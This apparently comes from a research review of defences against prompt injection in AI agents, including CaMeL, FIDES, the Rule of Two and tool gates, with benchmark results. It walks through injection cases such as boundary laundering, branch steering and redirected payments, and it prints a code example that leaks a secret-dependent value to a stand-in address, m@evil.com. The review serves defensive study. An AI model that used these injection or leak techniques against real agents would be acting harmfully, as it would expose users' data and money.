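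Jacob and colleagues built a stricter bug-fixing agent that passes on no free text from the bug report. Its quarantined model reads the report and returns file numbers, line numbers and choices from fixed lists, such as the type of bug. A planner that has not seen the report explores a clean copy of the code and writes three repair plans. A judge that has seen the report picks one and returns only its number. A separate agent then carries out the chosen plan.

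Jacob and colleagues tested the design with GPT-5.2 on 180 real bug reports. An injected instruction to create an extra file succeeded in 98.9% of runs without the defence and in none with it. But the number of bugs fixed fell from 123 (68.3%) to 81 (45.0%). They attribute the drop to the repairing agent no longer being able to read the reports' natural-language descriptions, which play a key role in repairing the bugs. An attacker can still direct the agent to the wrong part of the code. The fixed format took considerable testing to develop for this one job, so it is hard to see how a general-purpose agent could use a suitable format for every new request.

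### Limiting combinations of powers

These designs require a developer to build the agent around them. People who assemble an agent from ready-made tools need something simpler. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, advises them never to combine these three things:

- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content
- a way to communicate with the outside world

Under this rule, an agent may have any two of them. It may read private files and strangers' emails, for instance, if it cannot send anything out. That condition is hard to meet, because any web request can carry stolen data, even one that loads an image. A single tool may also combine all three powers. One connector for GitHub, a site where programmers share code, let an agent read public reports that anyone could file, access private projects, and publish changes that outsiders could see.

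The trifecta only concerns data theft, so an agent that reads strangers' emails and can delete the user's files passes the test if it cannot send anything out. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) covers more kinds of harm. It says that within one session an agent should be able to do at most two of three things: process untrustworthy input, access sensitive systems or private data, and change state or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three should run only under supervision, such as a person approving its actions.

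For an email assistant, Meta gives an example of removing each property:

| Property removed | What the assistant can still do |
|---|---|
| Untrustworthy input | Process emails from trusted senders only |
| Sensitive systems and private data | Work in a test environment without sensitive data |
| Changing state or communicating externally | Send emails only to trusted recipients, or after a person has checked the draft |

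An agent may also switch from one pair to another. For example, it could search the web first, then permanently lose its ability to communicate before it opens internal systems.

Willison (2025), in *Prompt injection*, a series of blog posts, welcomed the rule but objected that Meta's diagram marked every pair of properties as "safe", including untrustworthy input combined with the power to change state. That pair can do damage even without private data. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that "sensitive systems" means any system that matters to the user's security, so an agent without access to such systems can change only unimportant things, such as files in an isolated test environment. Meta changed the label to "lower risk". Ayzenberg's reply answers the objection, but the rule then depends on someone correctly listing the systems that matter.

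Restricting an assistant to trusted recipients also leaves a gap. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues had already warned that a hijacked assistant that can email only people in the same organisation could still ask a colleague to approve a security-sensitive action or ignore an alert. Meta says the rule does not cover misinformation in an agent's response, and users may approve a warning blindly.

Alhindi found another weakness, which appears when agents work as a team. In a test system for paying suppliers, five agents each obeyed the Rule of Two. One read suppliers' emails but had no private data and could not act. The other four had private data and could act, but did not read the emails. But the agents passed text to one another, so an instruction in an email could reach all of them. Four of the five broke the rule when this indirect exposure was counted.

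Alhindi then sent the team a malicious email with a genuine invoice and a request to change the supplier's bank details. The team changed them in 7 of 40 runs. The attacker received no money in these runs because the team had approved each invoice before changing the bank details, but the next payment would have gone to the account now on file. Alhindi then replaced the agent that read the emails with ordinary code that extracted only the invoice number, order number, total and supplier. In another 40 runs, the bank details never changed. Alhindi tested only one team, which used a small, older model, so the rate of 7 in 40 is weak evidence about other systems. But any team whose agents exchange free text can have the same flaw, and checking each agent separately will not find it.

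### The cost of choosing early

An agent is best protected when it chooses its actions before it reads anything untrusted. This doesn't limit the agent on the schedule request, because the request already determines the steps. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues are probably right that much email and calendar work is similar. It limits the agent most when the next step depends on what the agent reads, as when a user asks it to follow a project's setup instructions or to deal with whatever is in the inbox.

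*The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026) calls these context-dependent tasks. It compares 78 papers on attacks and defences and concludes that existing defences do not account for such tasks. A restricted design may therefore look less limiting in published tests than it would be for someone who often gives an agent this kind of work.

*ARGUS* (2026) argues that a defence that treats everything the agent reads as ordinary data will fail on these tasks, because the user's request is too vague to determine the action. It instead proposes letting the agent base decisions on what it reads, then checking whether the complete reasoning behind each action is benign. This could let the agent do many more tasks. But fixed rules usually can't determine whether reasoning is benign, and if a language model decides, an attacker can try to fool it.

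Even when a task's steps are predictable, tools can fail and early results can invalidate later steps. For this reason, *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025), a guide to plan-then-execute systems, calls a fixed plan "inherently brittle" and recommends letting a model revise the plan as the work proceeds. If that model reads untrusted results, an injection can add a call to the new plan, which the fixed plan was supposed to prevent. The agent could instead revise its plan using only a fixed set of error codes, or stop and ask the user. Either would preserve the protection, but the agent would handle fewer surprises by itself.

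## CaMeL: a gate that tracks where data came from

Even when an agent's plan is fixed, an attacker can still influence the values used in its actions, such as the account number on a bill. CaMeL, short for Capabilities for Machine Learning, adds a check on those values. Debenedetti and colleagues, from Google DeepMind and elsewhere, introduced it in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) wrote that he had seen "alarmingly little progress" on prompt injection in two and a half years, and that this paper changed that.

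### From a request to an allowed or blocked call

CaMeL builds on the code-then-execute design. A planning model that sees only the user's request and the tool descriptions writes a program in a restricted version of Python, and a quarantined model without tools reads untrusted content for it. CaMeL adds two parts:

1. An interpreter runs the program. It labels each value with where the value came from and who may read it. CaMeL calls these labels capabilities, though they work differently from the capabilities in Hardy's compiler story: they describe a piece of data, while Hardy's grant access to a file.
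2. Just before each tool call, a policy for that tool checks the labels on the arguments. As TechSpot explains, the interpreter can then block the call or ask the user to confirm it.

The labels follow a long tradition in computer security called information-flow control. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes its two usual kinds of label. An integrity label says whether data is trusted, and a confidentiality label says whether it is secret. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, also describe a finer confidentiality label that lists the permitted readers. If a value combines two documents, only people who may read both may read the result:

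{A, B, C} ∩ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

Integrity works the other way round, so one untrusted ingredient makes the whole result untrusted.

Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, give the example of a user who asks an agent to find meeting notes in Google Drive and send a summary to a particular employee. A simplified program for this task might be:

```
notes = drive.read("meeting notes")
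summary = quarantined_model("summarise", notes)
send_email("anna@company.com", summary)
```

Suppose that the user, Anna and Ben can read the notes, and that an outsider was able to edit them. The program then runs as follows:

1. The interpreter labels the notes as untrusted and readable by the user, Anna and Ben.
2. The summary gets the same label, because nobody can tell which parts of the notes influenced the model's output.
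3. The policy for sending email compares the recipient with the summary's permitted readers. Anna is one of them, so the email goes out.

If the user had named Carla, who has no access to the notes, the policy would stop the email. An instruction in the notes to send them to an outsider has no effect, because the program already fixes the recipient.

Now suppose the user asks the agent to send the summary to whoever is listed in the notes as project leader. The address comes from the notes, so CaMeL labels it untrusted. If the fixed plan were the only defense, the outsider could choose the recipient. Under a policy that requires a trusted recipient, CaMeL blocks the call or prompts the user to approve it, even if the address is correct.

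### The guarantee and its trusted base

Peters-Gill and colleagues split CaMeL's guarantee into two parts. The first is control-flow integrity, which means the agent's actions stay within a program that depends only on the user's request and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. Untrusted content may determine which of the program's existing branches runs, but it can't add a new one. The second is that every tool call satisfies the policies. Without any policies, only the first part remains.

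The guarantee depends on the user's request, the tools and their descriptions, the labels on incoming data, the policies and the interpreter. It holds even if an attacker completely controls the quarantined model's output. The planning model never receives the attacker's text, but it can still misinterpret the user's request and write a harmful program, and then only the policies can block the harmful actions.

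The interpreter has had flaws. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, show that it can lose track of a secret. Suppose a policy forbids emailing anything that depends on the user's bank balance to an outsider. The interpreter blocks a program that tests the balance and sends the email directly. It would allow a program like this one, which follows a pattern researchers have known about for decades:

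```
small = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold: small = False
if small: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the balance is above the threshold, the third line sets `small` to false and labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing. CaMeL updates a variable's label only when an assignment runs, so `rich` keeps its public label even though its value now depends on the balance. Because the label is public, CaMeL lets the email go out.

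An outsider can't write these lines into the program, because the planning model never reads the outsider's text. But a program written for a legitimate task could have the same structure. It might choose between two recipients based on an email's contents, and the chosen recipient could still be labeled trusted even though the email's author influenced the choice.

Garby and colleagues found a second leak, in the part of CaMeL that retries failed programs. The interpreter does not track this part. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and repeated attempts can reveal the rest. The researchers also found that inserting an untrusted value into a string could make the value count as trusted. Better code can fix these flaws, but they show that a soundly designed defence can still fail to deliver its guarantee.

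### What the AgentDojo scores measure

Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks with its security property, compared with 84% for an undefended system. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) gives a lower figure of 67%.

Two attacks succeeded in CaMeL's original evaluation, according to Garby and colleagues. In one, the user told the agent to make a payment based on a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. CaMeL's threat model excludes such cases, because the agent did what the user asked. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the benchmark's automatic check counted the quotation as a successful attack.

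Garby and colleagues also ran CaMeL themselves on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each. Policies made a large difference:

| CaMeL on the banking tasks | Tasks solved, GPT-5.2 | Tasks solved, MiMo-v2.5 | Successful attacks in completed runs, both models |
|---|---|---|---|
| Without policies | 66.7% | 70.8% | 5 of 622 |
| With policies | 37.5% | 37.5% | 0 of 588 |

They also cite another team's test on the 21 Slack tasks, in which CaMeL with policies solved seven. The Slack and banking results are hard to reconcile with 77% overall. Even if CaMeL had solved all 60 tasks in the other two parts of AgentDojo, its total would be about 75%. Differences in the models, the policies and the treatment of calls that need a user's approval could explain the gap, and the banking result is uncertain by about 27 percentage points either way. Still, the original average is not a good enough reason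 for a bank to expect to lose only seven percentage points of usefulness.

The banking results also show that much of the security comes from planning before reading. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needed an action that would never appear in a program written for the user's task. For example, an injection can't make an agent send money if its program only summarises recent transactions. The labels and policies matter in the other 47 combinations, where the planned actions could also carry out the attack. A security score for the whole test is therefore a poor measure of how well the policies work.

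One failure without policies came from a user's request to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planning model had no access to the file's contents, so it wrote a loop that read each instruction and called whichever tool it required. The program now allowed every possible action, and an attacker who edited the file could choose among them. Control-flow integrity still held, because the agent never left its program, but it no longer protected anything. When a user's request is open-ended, the planning model can itself write a program that removes this protection, and only policies can then limit the damage.

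### What an attacker can still do

CaMeL does not prevent harm through permitted actions, such as sending a false summary to the right person. Tallam and Miller describe a PDF containing a line that looks like a system instruction to forward the file to an outside address. If the agent repeats the line in its summary, the person reading it may follow the instruction. Tallam and Miller propose a second model to screen the agent's output, which could catch some cases but would be only a heuristic defence.

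CaMeL also trusts the user's message. Tallam and Miller point out that phishing or a persuasive chat message can get a user to give the agent an attacker's text. If the user pastes a stranger's email into the request, the planning model treats the email as part of the request and can write the stranger's instructions into the program. They propose screening requests for suspicious links, phrases and unusual text, which is another heuristic defence. A safer interface could have users attach outside text separately, so that the interpreter can label it as untrusted.

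Secrets can also leak through side channels. If a program contacts a website once for each unit of a secret number, anyone who can see the website's log can learn the number by counting the requests, even though no request contains it. Tallam and Miller give this example and also describe leaks through error messages and the time a program takes. They suggest capping such loops or combining the requests, and adding a strict mode that blocks actions that depend on a secret or asks the user about them.

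To avoid tiring users with approval requests, Tallam and Miller would allow read-only actions on open data after a basic check, ask for a light confirmation when untrusted data would change something in the user's own workspace, and demand stronger approval for payments, outside emails and other actions that are hard to undo. More untrusted data would then get through without the user being asked, so someone has to sort every action into the right group.

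### Who writes the policies

CaMeL needs a policy for each tool, and a sensible policy depends on the organisation. One company may let any employee receive a project summary, while another limits it to the project's team. Tallam and Miller warn that a company with hundreds of tools will end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules that nobody can audit as a whole. They recommend keeping the rules in one place, writing them in a language designed for access rules, and reusing common ones such as "share only within the company". Both work for a security company, and their paper does not test its proposals on a real deployment, but the same problem is familiar in other kinds of access control.

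Researchers often avoid writing policies for CaMeL. Ma and colleagues left it out of one of their benchmarks because it would have needed extensive policies for each group of tasks. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran it without policies, partly because any set they chose would have been arbitrary and would have determined the results. This is reasonable for a study of control flow, but it means that several of the published results for CaMeL test only the fixed program, not the gate that checks the data.

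Labeling the data also takes work. Costa and colleagues at Microsoft had to add labels to AgentDojo, and marked a data field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks used it. This gave a clear baseline, but it fitted the labels to the attacks being tested. A company can't know which fields future attackers will use, so it risks leaving openings by marking too few as untrusted or blocking ordinary work by marking too many.

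### FIDES and a planner that can look at results

Costa and colleagues' system, FIDES, lets the planning model choose one action at a time. After each tool call, the planner sees the trusted parts of the result. The system hides the untrusted parts in named variables, which the planner can pass to other tools without reading. The planner can also open a variable and react to what it reads, but then everything in its conversation counts as untrusted, and the policy blocks consequential actions from that point on.

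There is a compromise for small pieces of information. Suppose the user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if there is one:

1. The planner reads the emails, whose text stays hidden in a variable.
2. It asks a quarantined model whether they contain a meeting request, and allows only "yes" or "no" as an answer.
3. It opens the answer, which contains a single bit of untrusted information.
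4. If the answer is yes, it asks the quarantined model to extract the details into another hidden variable, and passes that variable to the calendar tool.

A policy can accept step 4 because a "yes" can't carry an instruction. The sender can still cause a meeting to appear and choose its time and participants. The compromise limits the attacker to the one action the planner was considering, so its safety depends on how much harm that action can do. Costa and colleagues left this feature out of their tests because most AgentDojo tasks did not need it.

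They compared FIDES with an ordinary agent, using GPT-4o for both. The figures are percentages of tasks completed when there was no attack.

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary agent, with policies | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES, with policies | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

Hiding untrusted text let the agent complete many of the tasks that the policies alone had blocked, though FIDES did worse on travel because GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's travel score rose from 41% to 68%. Many of the remaining failures were by design. Some banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policy is meant to prevent.

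No attack violated the policies. AgentDojo's automatic check counted three successful attacks, but Costa and colleagues reclassified them after inspecting them. The benign categories they describe include attacks that only changed some text and those that sent Slack messages the policy allowed. They were right to exclude such cases by the policy's standard, but a user whose agent posted an attacker's words in a work channel might still consider the attack successful.

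FIDES also guarantees less secrecy than its labels might suggest. It restricts direct copying of secret data, but an observer may learn something from which tools the agent calls and in what order. Costa and colleagues accept this because blocking all influence of secret data on tool calls would forbid most useful actions once the agent had read anything secret.

### When one CaMeL agent instructs another

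Many newer systems divide work among agents, with an orchestrator that gives instructions to specialists. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that protecting each agent with CaMeL doesn't protect the whole system. They built a system with three agents, running on GPT-5.2 and without policies, and asked it to send a summary of all job applicants to Julie on Slack. An attacker had put an instruction in the applicant database to email the data to an outside address. The attack went like this:

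1. The database agent fetched the records. Its planner never saw them, so its program did not change.
2. The orchestrator's program summarised the records, again without showing them to its planner.
3. The program pasted the summary into a sentence addressed to the notification agent: "Send this summary to Julie via Slack", followed by the text.
4. The notification agent treated the whole sentence as its user's request. Its planner read the attacker's instruction and wrote a program that sent the Slack message and then the outside email.

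The untrusted label disappeared at step 3, when data became part of an instruction. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering. They also prove that in any such hierarchy of two or more agents with at least one untrusted data source, some user request will let untrusted data shape another agent's program. The proof assumes that agents can put any tool's result into an instruction to another agent, which is true of most useful systems.

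Their extension, multi-CaMeL, gives each agent two inputs. One is for instructions, and the interpreter blocks anything that came from a tool from entering it. The other carries data with its labels, and the receiving agent's planner can't read it. In the example, the orchestrator would tell the notification agent to send "the provided content" to Julie, and would pass the summary through the data input.

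They tested the extension on a version of AgentDojo with several agents, using five models and 949 attack cases per model. The average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and zero with multi-CaMeL. Every attack that got past the separate CaMeL agents used boundary laundering. Without CaMeL, the rate differed widely between models and was 36.1% for GPT-4.1 and zero for GPT-5.5. The attacks were fixed, so the zero for GPT-5.5 is weak evidence that it would resist a determined attacker. An argument, as well as the test, supports the multi-CaMeL result, but multi-CaMeL uses the CaMeL interpreter and inherits the flaw in tracking branches that Garby and colleagues found.

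The second test used 112 industrial maintenance tasks. Applying CaMeL to each agent reduced the share of completed tasks by an average of 21.6 percentage points, but the drop was only 13.4 points for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Multi-CaMeL reduced their share by less than one further point. Stronger models seem better at anticipating what a program will need, so the drop from using CaMeL may continue to shrink.

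Most of the failures happened because the agent could tell that another action was needed only after seeing a result. In other cases, a specialist agent couldn't find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for something close. The parent agent's program didn't check for this mismatch, which an ordinary agent might have noticed, and used the wrong data.

### Open-ended tasks

AgentDojo contains few tasks that test this weakness. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) count only six of its 97 tasks as requiring the agent to make new plans partway through. They built a benchmark of 60 tasks that all require this, covering shopping, GitHub and daily life. For instance, a checkout page may tell the agent to log in first, or a site may send a one-time code by email. Each task also includes at least one helpful instruction from a third party, so an agent that ignores all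 such instructions will fail the task.

CaMeL completed none of the tasks with any of the four models in the main comparison. Without a defence, GPT-4o completed 53% and Claude 3.5 Sonnet 60%. The attack success rate against CaMeL was also zero, but that is easy to achieve when an agent completes no tasks. Li and colleagues attribute the result to CaMeL's fixed program.

That explanation is probably right for many of the tasks, but the score of zero may also reflect the setup. The benchmark needs its own policies, as Ma and colleagues noted when they decided against running CaMeL on it. CaMeL also depends on tool descriptions that state exactly what each tool returns, because the planner has to write code for a result it hasn't seen. The zero does show that the 77% on AgentDojo can't be extended to tasks of this kind, but it doesn't estimate how often CaMeL would fail in everyday use, because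 Li and colleagues chose tasks that require new plans.

Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) are more optimistic in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*. They adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer through its screen, where the next click seems to depend on what has just appeared. They argue that such work is more predictable than it looks. The planner can write branches in advance for cookie notices, failed clicks and other common events, and a quarantined model that sees the screen identifies which situation applies. The resulting programs averaged 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and four branches on AgentDojo. About half of the program went unused on any given run.

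They report that CaMeL kept up to 57% of the performance of a frontier model, Claude Sonnet 4.5. That is the share of the 109 tasks solved by the undefended agent that CaMeL also solved in at least one of five attempts. With a single attempt, it solved 28%. Five attempts are less useful outside a test, where someone has to tell which attempt worked and a failed one may already have sent a message or deleted a file. CaMeL used only 1.88 times as many tokens as the undefended agent, while a version based on FIDES used 29.6 times as many because it sent the planner the full history at every step.

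Policies are the harder problem for these agents. A policy can check the recipient of an email, but "click at this point on the screen" may mean log in, buy or delete, depending on what is there. Foerster and colleagues therefore ran their agent without policies and attacked it by influencing which branch of its program it took. They placed a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement. The program already contained a step for dismissing cookie notices, so the agent clicked on the advertisement and went to the attacker's website, even though the injection had added no action to the program. They call this branch steering. They tried two defences that cross-checked what was on the screen, and neither stopped it reliably.

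*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) presents COBRA, a system that commits in advance to what each branch may do, then checks the web requests and tool calls that result from the agent's clicks. These have a clearer meaning than the clicks themselves. A click on a fake cookie notice, for example, would produce a request to an unexpected website, which COBRA could refuse. COBRA blocked 1,289 of 1,312 attack cases from four published benchmarks. This suggests that a gate can work for computer use, provided that someone or something can predict which websites and tools each branch will need.

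### Whether CaMeL refutes the June 2025 claim

The claim by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, as worded, covers only defences that rely on language models. CaMeL does not contradict it, because CaMeL's interpreter and policies are ordinary code. But if an agent protected by CaMeL is still general-purpose, CaMeL would be a counterexample to the broader view that nobody can secure a general-purpose agent built on current models.

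There is a good case that a CaMeL agent is general-purpose. The planner writes a new program for each request, so nobody has to rebuild the agent. The same architecture has handled banking, travel bookings, office work and industrial maintenance, and with some changes it can operate a desktop computer. Within each area, users can ask for things the developers never anticipated.

The first of two objections is that the planner has to choose the steps before it sees the content, so its branches cover only what it anticipated. When the next step depends on unexpected content, the agent has to fail or ask the user, unless the planner writes a program that lets the content choose any tool, as it did with the banking file. Better planning models will anticipate more, and the results for GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5 suggest that this matters, but better models still can't write a specific program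 for instructions they haven't seen.

The second is that the guarantee covers only what the policies cover, and people have to write policies for every tool. An agent that connects to a new service without preparation would have no policy for it. The agent could refuse to use the service, which would make it less general, or use the service without a policy, which would leave only control-flow integrity. A planning model could draft the missing policy without reading untrusted content, so an injection could not corrupt the draft, but the model would then be part of the trusted base.

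CaMeL therefore refutes the broader view for the large class of requests whose possible steps a planner can write down in advance, using tools that have sound policies. These requests cover considerably more than an agent with one narrow job can do, but people usually expect a general-purpose agent to also read something unexpected and work out what to do next.

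## Four gates compared on the same attacks

CaMeL changes how an agent plans. A developer can instead let an ordinary agent choose each step after reading the last result, and put a gate between the agent and its tools. The protection then depends on the gate's rules and the code that applies them. In November 2026, Aljumaily and colleagues compared four deterministic gates with prompt warnings, a detector and human approval, using the same 13 tasks and 12 tools.

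For every defence, an attack counted as successful if the agent carried out an action with side effects that the user's request did not authorise. The code that checked this used no input from the defence. Five of the twelve tools only read things such as emails, files and web pages. The other seven can do damage by sending email, posting data to the web, writing or deleting files, changing configurations, running shell commands and setting target values for industrial equipment.

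### From tool names to task-bound permissions

| Gate | What it checks | Attack variants admitted, out of 33 |
|---|---|---|
| Tool allow-list | Whether the task may use this tool | 27 |
| Naive argument checks | Also the arguments, such as recipients and file paths | 18 |
| Hardened argument checks | The same, with protection against disguised arguments | 6 |
| Task-bound permissions | Whether the request authorises this action with these arguments, plus a rule against sending out confidential data | 1 |

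These counts involve no language model. Aljumaily and colleagues ran each gate's code on 33 attack variants that would have had an unauthorised effect.

The naive and hardened gates differ mainly in how well they were programmed. Many of the disguises are old tricks. A web address can begin with "company.com@" and lead to a different site, because browsers treat the text before the @ as a username. A file path can start in a permitted folder and then leave it with "../". An attacker can also add a second recipient to an email, or a second command after a permitted one.

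A fixed set of attacks can hide this difference. In simulation, an attacker who varied the arguments over up to 25 attempts beat the hardened gate in 30.8% of campaigns and the naive gate in 84.6%, about the same rate as against the allow-list. Simulated attackers who did not vary the arguments did equally well against both gates. A buyer who tests a gate only with ready-made injections could easily buy the naive version.

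The strictest gate's score is partly a result of the test's design, because the gate permits the same set of actions that the judging code treats as authorised. The score shows what a gate can do when somebody has written a perfect policy for every task. Damage rose steadily as the policy became less complete. On a scale from 0 to 10 for the worst unauthorised action, a compromised model averaged 0.69 with all the rules in place, 1.62 when each rule had an 80% chance of being included, and 5.32 when that chance was 40%.

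### Two real models

Aljumaily and colleagues then used two open models as the agent, the 1.5-billion-parameter and 7-billion-parameter versions of Qwen2.5. They ran each model through 156 attack episodes per defence. The table gives the share of episodes in which the agent achieved the attacker's goal.

| Defence | 1.5B model | 7B model |
|---|---|---|
| None | 66% | 86% |
| Warning in the prompt | 65% | 55% |
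| Warning and spotlighting | 42% | 40% |
| Spotlighting and a detector | 10% | 0% |
| Tool allow-list | 42% | 67% |
| Naive argument checks | 10% | 21% |
| Hardened argument checks | 9% | 22% |
| Task-bound permissions | 1.3% | 7.7% |

With the strictest gate in place, the models still proposed the attacker's call in 64% and 84% of episodes, so the gate, rather than the models, stopped most of the attacks. Two attacks got through with the smaller model and 12 with the larger, all in one task where the injection made the agent write a false report on pressure. The gate allowed the agent to write that report, so how often the attack succeeded depended on the model. If the 156 episodes were spread evenly over the 13 tasks, the larger model falsified the report every time. The true rates may be higher, because the judging code counted a report as false only if it contained the attacker's exact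 phrase.

The strictest gate did not reduce either model's completion rate on attack-free tasks. The larger model completed 99% with or without it. The smaller model completed 71% with the gate, up from 50% without it, because the gate blocked unauthorised calls that the model made by mistake. But these figures also depend on having the right policy for each task.

The detector's 0% with the larger model looks better than the gate's 7.7%. It also contradicts the paper's simulation, in which every warning and detector fails in 100% of long campaigns. That 100% follows from the simulation's assumption that warnings and detectors weaken as an attacker keeps trying, and the real runs do not support it for the detector. The real runs don't show that the detector is safe either, because their attacks were not adapted to it. When Nasr and colleagues adapted their attacks to four other detectors,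 the attacks succeeded in at least 71% of scenarios.

A separate test on the smaller model undermined another assumption, that attacks can be ranked on a single scale from weak to strong. An injection that invoked the document's owner worked 50% of the time, while one styled as an urgent system notice worked 4% of the time. Both models are tiny by 2026 standards, so their rates don't show how often a leading model would follow injected instructions.

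### A fully compromised model

To test the worst case, the simulation replaces the language model with a program that always obeys the attacker and tries every attack in the library. With the task-bound gate in place, this program never took a severe action, such as running a shell command, posting data to an outside site or changing an equipment setting. It still did something unauthorised in 23.1% of episodes, the equivalent of three tasks out of 13, mostly by putting false content into files that the agent had permission to write.

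The average damage of 0.69 out of 10 can understate the harm, because the score depends on the tool and ignores the content. Writing a file counts as 3, whatever the file contains. At an industrial plant, a report that lists a dangerous pressure as normal could do much more damage than that. Aljumaily and colleagues acknowledge the problem and advise operators who take false content more seriously to send more of these actions for human review. Checking the arguments more strictly would not help, because the file name and the tool are both correct.

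### Human approval and its budget

Aljumaily and colleagues tested human review only in simulation. Their simulated reviewer catches 90% of unauthorised calls at first, then fewer as the workload grows and the requests keep coming.

Without a gate, this reviewer gave no protection against the compromised model, which achieved a severe action in every episode. Even a reviewer who never tired let one through in 92.6% of episodes. Repetition alone can do this. If a reviewer independently misses 10% of bad requests, the chance of approving at least one out of 25 is

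1 − 0.9^25 ≈ 93%

An approval budget limits the agent to a fixed number of approval requests per episode. Ordinary code refuses any further requests without showing them to anyone. The figures below are for the simulated reviewer without a gate.

| Requests allowed per episode | Episodes with a severe action | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 17.3% | 95.4% |
| 2 | 37.4% | 99.4% |
| 4 | 73.2% | 99.5% |
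| 8 | 97.8% | 99.5% |
| No limit | 100% | 99.5% |

The budget restores a bound by giving the attacker only a few chances, but the bound depends on how good the reviewer is. The budget also resets with each episode, so an attacker who can reach the agent again gets more chances. An attacker who only wants to be a nuisance can use up the budget so that the user's legitimate requests fail.

Human review of severe actions added nothing to the task-bound gate, which had already blocked the bad ones. Reviewing less severe actions when the agent had read untrusted content reduced the share of episodes with an unauthorised action from 23.1% to 8.7%, and required 0.57 approval requests per ordinary task. This reduction assumes that the reviewer can recognise a false report, but someone who has asked an agent for the pressure may not know what it should be.

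Real reviewers may be much worse than the simulated one. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, who worked on coding tasks and approved the agent's commands. In each session, the experimenters replaced one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. With reviewers like these, even a budget of one request would let a dangerous command through about 86% of the time.

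The study supports a product that Anthropic sells, since the company's model-based gate blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers had no code of their own at stake, and a developer looking after a company's live database would probably read more carefully. But the artificial setting alone does not easily explain the drop over a session, which is what one would expect from fatigue.

Evidence from ordinary use supports the same conclusion, though less clearly. Claude Code users accepted 93% of permission prompts according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, published in March 2026, and 97% according to the August article. Most prompts are for harmless commands, so a careful user would also accept nearly all of them. But users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented for approval. People may pay more attention to a few large decisions than to hundreds of small ones, though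 they may also reject a plan simply because it is a poor way to do the job.

Frequent approval prompts can also lead users to weaken the gate. By June 2026, almost half of the active command-line users of Claude Code had written a rule that let some shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules allowed any Python or Node program, which Anthropic considers practically equivalent to allowing every command.

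In auto mode, Anthropic uses a fixed limit similar to an approval budget. After the classifier refuses three actions in a row, or 20 in a session, the agent has to stop and involve the user. This keeps a hijacked agent from trying variations indefinitely, but the user may then approve the next action out of habit.

### The right call with the attacker's argument

The task-bound gate could detect a wrong argument because the researchers had given it the right one. In ordinary use, the right argument may be in something the agent hasn't read yet. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay the recipient named in a bill, and an injection in another document asks for the same payment to a different account. The attacker's payment would use the right tool and amount, and only the account number would be wrong.

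*ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) calls this within-tool hijacking. By its count, 524 of AgentDojo's 629 injection tests require a tool that the user's task does not need. Another 85 use only tools the task needs but change an argument, and the other 20 fit neither group. A gate that checked only tool names could therefore stop 83% of AgentDojo's attacks and still let an attacker redirect every payment. Within-tool hijacking is more common in the banking tests, where it accounts for 42 of 144.

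*ClawGuard* (Zhao, Li and colleagues, April 2026) introduces a gate that generally cannot make this distinction. A language model drafts rules from the user's request before the agent calls any tool, the user confirms them, and ordinary code enforces them. The rules cover tools, shell commands, file paths and web domains. They can separate a permitted folder from the one that holds the user's passwords, or a known website from an attacker's. But they have no field for a payment's recipient or amount, so the rules treat the two payments alike.

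Zhao and colleagues report that no AgentDojo attack succeeded against any of five models with ClawGuard. The models already resisted more than 95% of these attacks without it, so ClawGuard had few of them left to stop. In the security tests, ClawGuard also refused every call it would normally have sent to the user for approval. With this setting, agents kept 87.4% of their usual performance on ordinary tasks, compared with 95.1% when up to three approvals were allowed. Nobody tested the attacks with a person approving calls, so the security results don't cover the setting that kept 95.1% of performance.

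ClawGuard did worse in a later comparison. *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026), the August study of runtime authorisation, tested it with two weaker models on AgentDojo and AgentDyn. Attacks succeeded in 4.3% to 7.0% of cases, down from 16% to 33% without a defence. Missing rules for arguments could explain many of the remaining successes, but the study does not break them down by cause.

ToolFence can make the distinction when the request specifies where the argument should come from. A language model writes a permission for each expected action, using only the request and trusted tool descriptions. For the bill, the permission allows one payment, and requires the amount to match the request and the account number to come from the bill file. Ordinary code then checks each call. It refuses the attacker's account number because the number came from another document, and it refuses a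 second payment to the correct account.

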